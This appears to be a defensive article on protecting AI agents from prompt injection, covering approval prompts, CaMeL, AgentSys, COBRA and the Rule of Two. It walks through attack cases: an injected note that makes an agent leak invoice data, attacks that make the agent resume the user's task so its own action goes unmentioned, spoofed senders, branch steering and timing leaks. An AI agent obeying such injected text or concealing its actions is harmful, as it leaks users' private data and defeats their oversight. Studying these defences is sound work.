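An attacker can make the user more likely to approve the final request by making it look ordinary. In an example from Hossain and colleagues, a user asks an agent to reconcile supplier invoices and send the auditor only the totals. An injected instruction in a supplier's note causes the agent to copy the full invoice data into a file called report.csv. Several steps later, the agent asks for permission to send report.csv to the auditor. The user knows the auditor and was expecting a report, so nothing in the permission request looks wrong, even though the file contains more than the totals.

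Commands can hide their effects in a similar way. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyses 290 reports of agents damaging people's files, and finds that problems with user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of these, the agent had automatic approval, in some cases because the user was tired of answering hundreds of prompts. In 31, the prompt didn't give enough information. For example, a prompt might ask to run a set-up script by name, which tells the user nothing about what is in the script. (Some reports involved both problems.)

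The approval software can also have flaws. In versions of OpenClaw before 2026.2.22, approving one harmless command could let later commands run without approval, according to OpenClaw's security advisory. Approval problems were also the most common kind on PromptArmor's list.

Someone who approves a harmful action may not learn about it afterwards. *Will the User Ever Know?* (Lee, Kim and Lee, 2026) examined 2,087 successful attacks to see why some agents mentioned the attacker's action in their final reply and others didn't. The reply tended to describe whatever the agent had done last. In 68% of the hidden attacks, which the reply didn't mention, the agent returned to the user's task after carrying out the attacker's, while in 71% of the visible ones it stopped after the attacker's task. Extending existing attacks with an instruction to return to the user's task raised the rate of hidden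 successes by up to 24 percentage points. An approval prompt may therefore be the user's only chance to notice such an attack.

### Asking only about rare, irreversible actions

If people stop paying attention after dozens of prompts, one remedy is to prompt them less often. The ordinary tasks in *LivePI* involved 899 tool calls, of which the rules selected eight for review. The most effective prompt in the experiment by Hossain and colleagues took a median of 33 seconds. At that rate, reviewing all 899 calls would take more than eight hours, and reviewing only the eight would take less than five minutes.

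But fewer prompts don't necessarily make people more careful. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?* (Yan, 2026), 113 people who don't work in software supervised an agent through a simulated day. Seven of the agent's 18 actions went beyond what they had asked for, such as reading their bank transactions. One group approved or refused every action. Another first set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four kinds of action, such as spending money.

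The rules reduced the average number of prompts from 18 to about 11, but people with rules blocked only 40% of the unwanted actions, while the group that reviewed everything blocked 60%. Most of the rules people chose were "ask", and when the agent then asked about an unwanted action, they approved it 67% of the time, compared with 40% for the group without rules. It isn't clear why, but people who had already set a rule may have felt they had dealt with the risk.

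Yan's result is a good reason not to assume that standing rules will protect people. It is weaker evidence against asking rarely, because participants with rules still answered about 11 prompts in around 11 minutes. The unwanted actions also came from the agent itself rather than an attacker, and some were mild, such as a call to the airport to confirm a flight, which nearly everyone approved.

A stronger reason for asking only about irreversible actions is that the owner can undo the others. The owner can restore an earlier version of a badly edited document, or recover a deleted folder from a backup that the agent can't reach, but can't recall a bank statement that the agent has emailed to a stranger. An owner could let the agent carry out actions that are easy to undo, and require approval only for payments, permanent deletions and sending private data to new recipients. *Let the Agent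 Do It?* (2026), a study of how software practitioners make these decisions, suggests that approval prompts should show whether an action can be undone.

Some actions don't need a prompt because the agent should never take them. Anthropic's automatic reviewer is designed never to approve sending code or secrets to an outside destination. Users who want to do this have to leave the automatic mode or run the command themselves. OpenClaw's documentation also describes an optional automatic reviewer for commands that aren't on the owner's list. This can reduce the number of prompts, but if the reviewer is a language model, planted text might fool it too. If the reviewer runs on a hosted service, the owner of a local model is also sending the model's commands to another company.

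This approach can still fail when an irreversible action is the last of several harmless-looking steps, as with the auditor's report. The harness could help by recording which files the agent used to make each new one. Hossain and colleagues built a monitor that does this, and it detected 89% of 120 violations. When they let it block actions automatically, the share of tests in which an agent did something forbidden fell from 43% to 5%. That result is for one agent, but it suggests software can catch some of the cases that people find hardest.

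The owner of an inbox assistant like Triggs's could let it read mail and write drafts freely, but require approval before it sends an attachment to an unfamiliar address. The approval request should identify the bank statement and the recipient, and show that the agent is acting on an email from that recipient. It should also reach the owner through a channel that the email's sender can't use, and the harness should treat no answer as a refusal.

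## CaMeL, a design that keeps untrusted text from choosing actions

*Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (Debenedetti, Shumailov and colleagues, 2025) introduced CaMeL, a design from Google DeepMind in which a model chooses the actions before any part of the system reads untrusted text. The rules that protected OpenClaw in *LivePI* instead check an action after the model has read such text.

### Two models with different jobs

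CaMeL builds on an earlier proposal. Willison, in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants* (2023), divided an assistant into two models. One of them, the planner, takes the user's request and can use tools. The other, the quarantined model, reads untrusted text and has no tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, passes material between them. If the user wants a summary of the latest email, this happens:

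1. The planner tells the controller to fetch the email. The controller stores it under the name $VAR1 without showing it to the planner.
2. The planner requests a summary of $VAR1. The controller gives the email to the quarantined model and stores the answer as $VAR2.
3. The planner tells the controller to display $VAR2, still without having read it.

An instruction in the email can fool the quarantined model, but that model can only write text. The reader agent that OpenClaw's developers recommend gives less protection because the main agent reads its summary. In Willison's pattern, the planner may see an answer only if the controller can verify it, for example by checking that it is one of a fixed set of categories.

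Willison called his own solution "pretty bad". It is complicated to build, and a single mistake that lets untrusted text reach the planner undoes the protection. Debenedetti and colleagues found another weakness. Even if the planner never reads the email, its actions can still use a name or address that the quarantined model took from it.

### Sending Anna's file

Suppose that a user tells the assistant to send the file Anna asked for to the address in her email. In CaMeL, the planner first turns this request into a short program in a restricted form of Python. A simplified version could look like this:

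```
email   = find_email(sender="Anna")
name    = ask_quarantined("Which file does she want?", email)
address = ask_quarantined("Where should it go?", email)
file    = find_file(name)
send_email(to=address, attachment=file)
```

An interpreter, which is ordinary software, then runs the program and keeps a record of where each value came from. Strangers can write to the inbox, so the email is untrusted, and so are the file name and the address that the quarantined model found in it. If the interpreter computes a value v from the values v₁ to vₖ, then

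sources(v) = sources(v₁) ∪ … ∪ sources(vₖ).

An untrusted value therefore stays untrusted however the program processes it. The interpreter can also record who may read each value. Debenedetti and colleagues call these labels capabilities, which is where the "Ca" in CaMeL comes from. (Hardy's capabilities were references that granted access to a file, so the word has a somewhat different meaning here.)

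Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the labels against a policy. Willison explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025) that a policy might let the assistant send email to known, trusted addresses and require the user's approval for any other. A second rule could check whether the recipient is allowed to read the attachment.

Now suppose that an attacker has sent an email under Anna's name, and the program finds it instead of the real one:

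| What the attacker wants | Does the fixed program prevent it? | Does the policy prevent it? |
|---|---|---|
| Delete the Documents folder | Yes, it has no step that deletes anything | Not needed |
| Forward the whole inbox | Yes, it has no step that does this | Not needed |
| Have the file sent to the attacker's address | No | Yes, unless the user approves the address |
| Have a bank statement sent to Anna instead of the file she wanted | No | Yes, if it records that Anna may not read the statement |

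The first two attacks fail even if the quarantined model obeys every instruction it reads. In the notation used for Triggs's test, p could be 100% and the attacker would still get only some influence over the five steps in this program, rather than A, the full set of things the agent can do.

In the last two attacks, the program runs exactly as the planner wrote it, but with values the attacker supplied. Only the policy can stop these attacks, and it can't distinguish the attacker's address from a legitimate new one. If Anna has changed jobs and written from an unfamiliar account, her address has the same label as the attacker's, so the user has to decide.

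Security then depends heavily on what the user approves. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) uses proof-checking software to verify what various defences guarantee. In one example, a user approves the assistant's next use of the email tool, intending it for her reply. An injected instruction uses the approval first to send her private data, and the system then blocks her reply because the approval is gone. If she approves the exact message instead, the injected call can send only that message.

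### The cost in finished tasks

The usual test for such designs is AgentDojo, a set of 97 simulated tasks in banking, travel, workplace chat and office work, with 629 attack cases. Debenedetti and colleagues report that CaMeL completed 77% of the tasks, compared with 84% for an undefended system.

An independent test found a much higher cost. Wen, Xiao and colleagues (2026), in *AGENTSYS*, ran several defences with GPT-4o mini, a small hosted model from 2024, and compared them with a design of their own:

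| Design | Tasks completed without an attack | Attacks that worked | Tokens used |
|---|---|---|---|
| No defence | 63.5% | 30.7% | 0.82 million |
| CaMeL | 30.0% | 0% | 6.09 million |
| AgentSys | 64.4% | 0.8% | 3.25 million |

In tests by Wen and colleagues, CaMeL stopped every attack but completed fewer than half as many tasks as the undefended agent and used about seven times as many tokens. Wen and colleagues had a reason to want their own design to look better, though they used CaMeL's published code. The choice of model probably explains much of the difference from CaMeL's original result. A CaMeL planner has to write a correct program for data it can't see, which is harder than choosing each step after seeing the result of the last.

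The 0% attack success rate means little without the task completion rate, because an agent that does nothing would also score 0%. IsolateGPT, another design in the same test, stopped every attack but completed only 6% of the tasks. The better argument for CaMeL is that its structure protects against unplanned actions, so this protection doesn't depend on which attacks the testers tried. That matters because the attacks in *The Attacker Moves Second* succeeded over 90% of the time against most of the 12 defences tested, according to Willison's *New prompt injection papers* (2025).

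### When the next step depends on the text

The planner can't write a program in advance for some requests. If the user says "do what Anna asks in her email", the right action depends on whether Anna wants a file, a meeting or a refund. The planner would have to read the email to find out, which CaMeL is designed to prevent.

Open-ended requests are also the easiest for attackers to exploit. *AutoDojo* (2026) groups banking tasks by how much the user left open and reports how often attacks succeeded against an undefended agent using Gemini 2.5 Flash. The success rate was 67% on the most open tasks, 23% on the middle group and 14% on the fully specified ones. So some of the usefulness that CaMeL gives up comes from tasks that were already unusually dangerous.

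AgentSys keeps more of this flexibility. Its main agent still decides each step after the last one returns a result, but it receives only the fields it specified before calling the tool, such as a name and an email address. A temporary worker agent reads the raw text and fills in those fields. If the worker tries to take an action of its own, such as sending a message, a separate model first compares the action with the user's request, also without seeing the raw text.

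The weak point of AgentSys is that a field can hold any text, so an attacker could write an instruction where the worker expects a name, and the main agent would read it. When Wen and colleagues used an automated system to refine attacks against AgentSys, the attacks' overall success rate rose from 0.8% to 2.1%, and in the banking tasks it reached 6.9%. The full design is still far safer than the undefended agent, but it offers no guarantee like CaMeL's. It also reduces the number of tasks completed, even with a better model. With GPT-5.1, AgentSys lowered the share of successful attacks from 3.8% to 0.3% and the share of completed tasks from 85% to 75%.

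*Twin Agent* (2026) describes a similar compromise in which one agent explores the untrusted material and sends short hints to a second agent, which acts. Capping the length of the hints limits how much an attacker can communicate to the second agent. This design also has no formal guarantee.

### Agents that use a screen

A computer-use agent works by viewing screenshots and clicking. This is awkward for CaMeL because the planner can't predict what will be on the screen. A cookie notice might cover the page, or the browser might already be open at another site.

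*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) had the planner write a program with a branch for each situation it could predict. The program has a quarantined model describe the screen, checks the description against a prediction such as "a cookie notice is visible", and takes the matching branch. These programs averaged 41 tool calls and 40 branches, compared with about five tool calls and four branches for AgentDojo tasks. Roughly half the steps were fallbacks that never ran.

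Foerster and colleagues say that this design retains up to 57% of a leading model's performance. The figure comes from 109 tasks, the same number that Claude Sonnet 4.5 had completed without the design. With it, the agent completed 62 of them in at least one of five attempts, but only 31 (28%) on the first. A user would normally get the first attempt, unless something could pick the best of five plans. The design used 1.88 times the tokens, a modest increase, perhaps because an ordinary computer-use agent already calls its model at every step.

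A fixed program with many branches also gives attackers a new opportunity, because they can influence which branch runs. In one attack that Foerster and colleagues tried, an advertisement contained a fake cookie notice. The program had a step for closing cookie notices, so the agent clicked on the advertisement and landed on the attacker's site. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering, and it worked without any instruction changing the program. They had left out CaMeL's policies because a click has no fixed meaning for a policy to check. The same click can open a tab or confirm a bank transfer.

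Zingrillo, Foerster and colleagues (2026), in *Securing Computer-Use Agents Against Branch Steering Attacks*, moved the checks from the click to the network request it causes. Before the agent sees any web page, the planner in their system, COBRA, limits which sites each branch may contact, which tools it may use and which values it may send. Software between the agent and the network blocks everything else. If the task needs an important value, such as an account number, that neither the user nor an approved source has given, COBRA asks the user for it during planning.

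In the paper's tests, attacks succeeded 89.5% of the time against a fixed program without limits and never against COBRA, which kept 97% of the fixed program's usefulness. The 97% figure doesn't account for the usefulness the agent had already lost by planning in advance. An attack counted as successful only if the harmful action broke the limits in force at that moment, which COBRA is designed to enforce. Steering the agent to a bad choice within those limits, such as the wrong product in an approved shop, would not have counted.

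### False summaries, policies and timing

No version of this design ensures that the quarantined model's output is accurate. An email can still distort a summary, and the program will display the result as planned. Willison described an attack in which the displayed text persuades the user to copy a block of scrambled private data into a website. Policies on tool calls don't apply because the user, not the assistant, sends the data. The interface could at least mark the summary as derived from outside text, since the interpreter tracks its source.

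Someone also has to write the policies and keep them up to date. Debenedetti and colleagues list this among CaMeL's limitations, along with the risk that users tire of approval requests. A strict policy would interrupt the user for every new address, while a loose one would let Anna's impostor through. Willison doubts that ordinary users can manage such policies, and says he still finds permission systems hard to reason about after two decades in application security. COBRA's planner writes the limits itself, which saves work but lets a planning mistake become a security mistake.

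Finally, a program can reveal private data without sending it, through what security engineers call a side channel. Suppose it downloads one picture from a supplier's website for each unpaid invoice. The supplier never receives the invoices but can learn how many are unpaid by counting the downloads.

Dongol found a timing leak in the example where the user approves an exact message. The attacker's instruction tells the model to send a private value. The software blocks that value if it differs from the approved reply, and the reply goes out at its usual time. If the two are identical, the message goes out one step early, so an attacker who can measure the timing learns whether they match. This reveals very little at a time and would be a minor worry for most households compared with an emailed bank statement.

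Dongol's proofs cover only leaks. Under their definition, an agent is secure if injected text doesn't let an attacker learn more than they could from the same program with a model that ignores such text. The proofs don't address an attack that deletes a folder, because it reveals nothing.

### Can a small local model write the plan?

Because the planner never sees the user's files or email, people who want privacy could have a hosted model write the program and a small local model read the private text. When Triggs used GPT-5 nano, OpenAI received the financial documents, but with this arrangement it would have received only the request to summarise a new email. COBRA's tests used this combination, with GPT-5 as the planner and UI-TARS-1.5-7B, an open-weight model with 7 billion parameters, reading the screen on local hardware.

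This doesn't help someone who wants no hosted model or whose computer is offline. They need a local planner, and the evidence on those is discouraging. Foerster and colleagues compared nine planners on 17 tasks. GPT-5 completed 12 and Grok-4 came second with 10, so the three open-weight planners each completed at most 10, and all three are far too large for a gaming PC. The choice of model for reading the screen mattered much less. The agent completed 65% of 60 tasks within five attempts when the 7-billion-parameter model read the screen, compared with 68% when Claude Sonnet 4.5 did.

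The nearest thing to a test of a small planner comes from Wen and colleagues, who ran AgentSys with Qwen2.5-7B, a model about the size of the one on Triggs's PC:

| Qwen2.5-7B | Without AgentSys | With AgentSys |
|---|---|---|
| All tasks completed | 38% | 26% |
| Office tasks completed | 45% | 7.5% |
| Attacks that worked | 14% | 3.5% |

The office tasks involve email, calendars and files, much like the work people give OpenClaw. The model completed 18 of the 40 tasks without the defence and three with it. CaMeL would probably be harder still, since its planner has to write the whole program at once. Newer small models should do better than Qwen2.5-7B, which dates from 2024, but only testing on a user's own tasks would show whether one can run a personal assistant this way.

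An owner with a small model could avoid the problem by writing the programs by hand. Triggs's scheduled task always had the same steps, and only the last one, the summary, needed a model.

### Splitting the powers between sessions

A simpler approach is to make sure that no single session has every dangerous power. Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) says that, until models can reliably detect and refuse injected instructions, an agent working without supervision should have at most two of these three properties in a session:

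- **A:** it processes untrusted input.
- **B:** it has access to sensitive systems or private data.
- **C:** it can change things or communicate with the outside.

Triggs's assistant had all three. Meta describes a similar email assistant and gives three ways to fix it. The assistant could read mail only from trusted senders, which removes A. It could work in a test environment with no private data, which removes B. Or it could send messages only to trusted recipients, or only after a person has checked the draft, which restricts C. An owner can do most of this with settings and separate accounts, without an interpreter or a planner that writes code, so it suits a local model of any size.

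Willison welcomed the rule because C, unlike the last part of his lethal trifecta, also includes actions such as deleting files. But he soon objected that Meta's diagram marked combining A and C as safe, even though an agent that reads strangers' text and can change things could do harm without access to private data. The rule's developers accepted this, changed the diagram and described the rule as a minimum standard.

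The Cline attack shows how easy it is to misjudge an agent under this rule. The agent that read GitHub issues clearly had A and C. It also had B, because it could reach the publishing keys through the shared cache, but a developer who looked only at its access token could reasonably have decided that it didn't.

Meta allows an agent to change its combination partway through a session. For example, it could browse the web first, then permanently lose its ability to communicate before it opens internal files. Dongol's proofs support such a switch but show that the order matters. The safest time to remove the tools an injection could use is before the agent reads any untrusted text. An agent that reads a hostile email first can leak any private data already in its memory, even if it loses its email tool before opening more private data. Meta's example is therefore safe only if the session starts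 without private data.

Separate sessions can also affect each other through what they save. If one session reads a hostile web page and writes notes, and another reads those notes with access to the owner's files and email, the attacker's text has reached an agent that has B and C. The second session should treat the notes as untrusted, but it may have no way to determine their source. CaMeL's interpreter tracks where data came from within a program, while the Rule of Two leaves that tracking to the developer.

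Sending Anna the file would take two sessions under this rule. In the first, the agent reads her email and reports which file she wants and where to send it, but it can't send anything. The user then starts a second session, which can send files but not read the inbox, and types in the file name and address. This takes longer than CaMeL would, and it protects the user only if they check the address before typing it.
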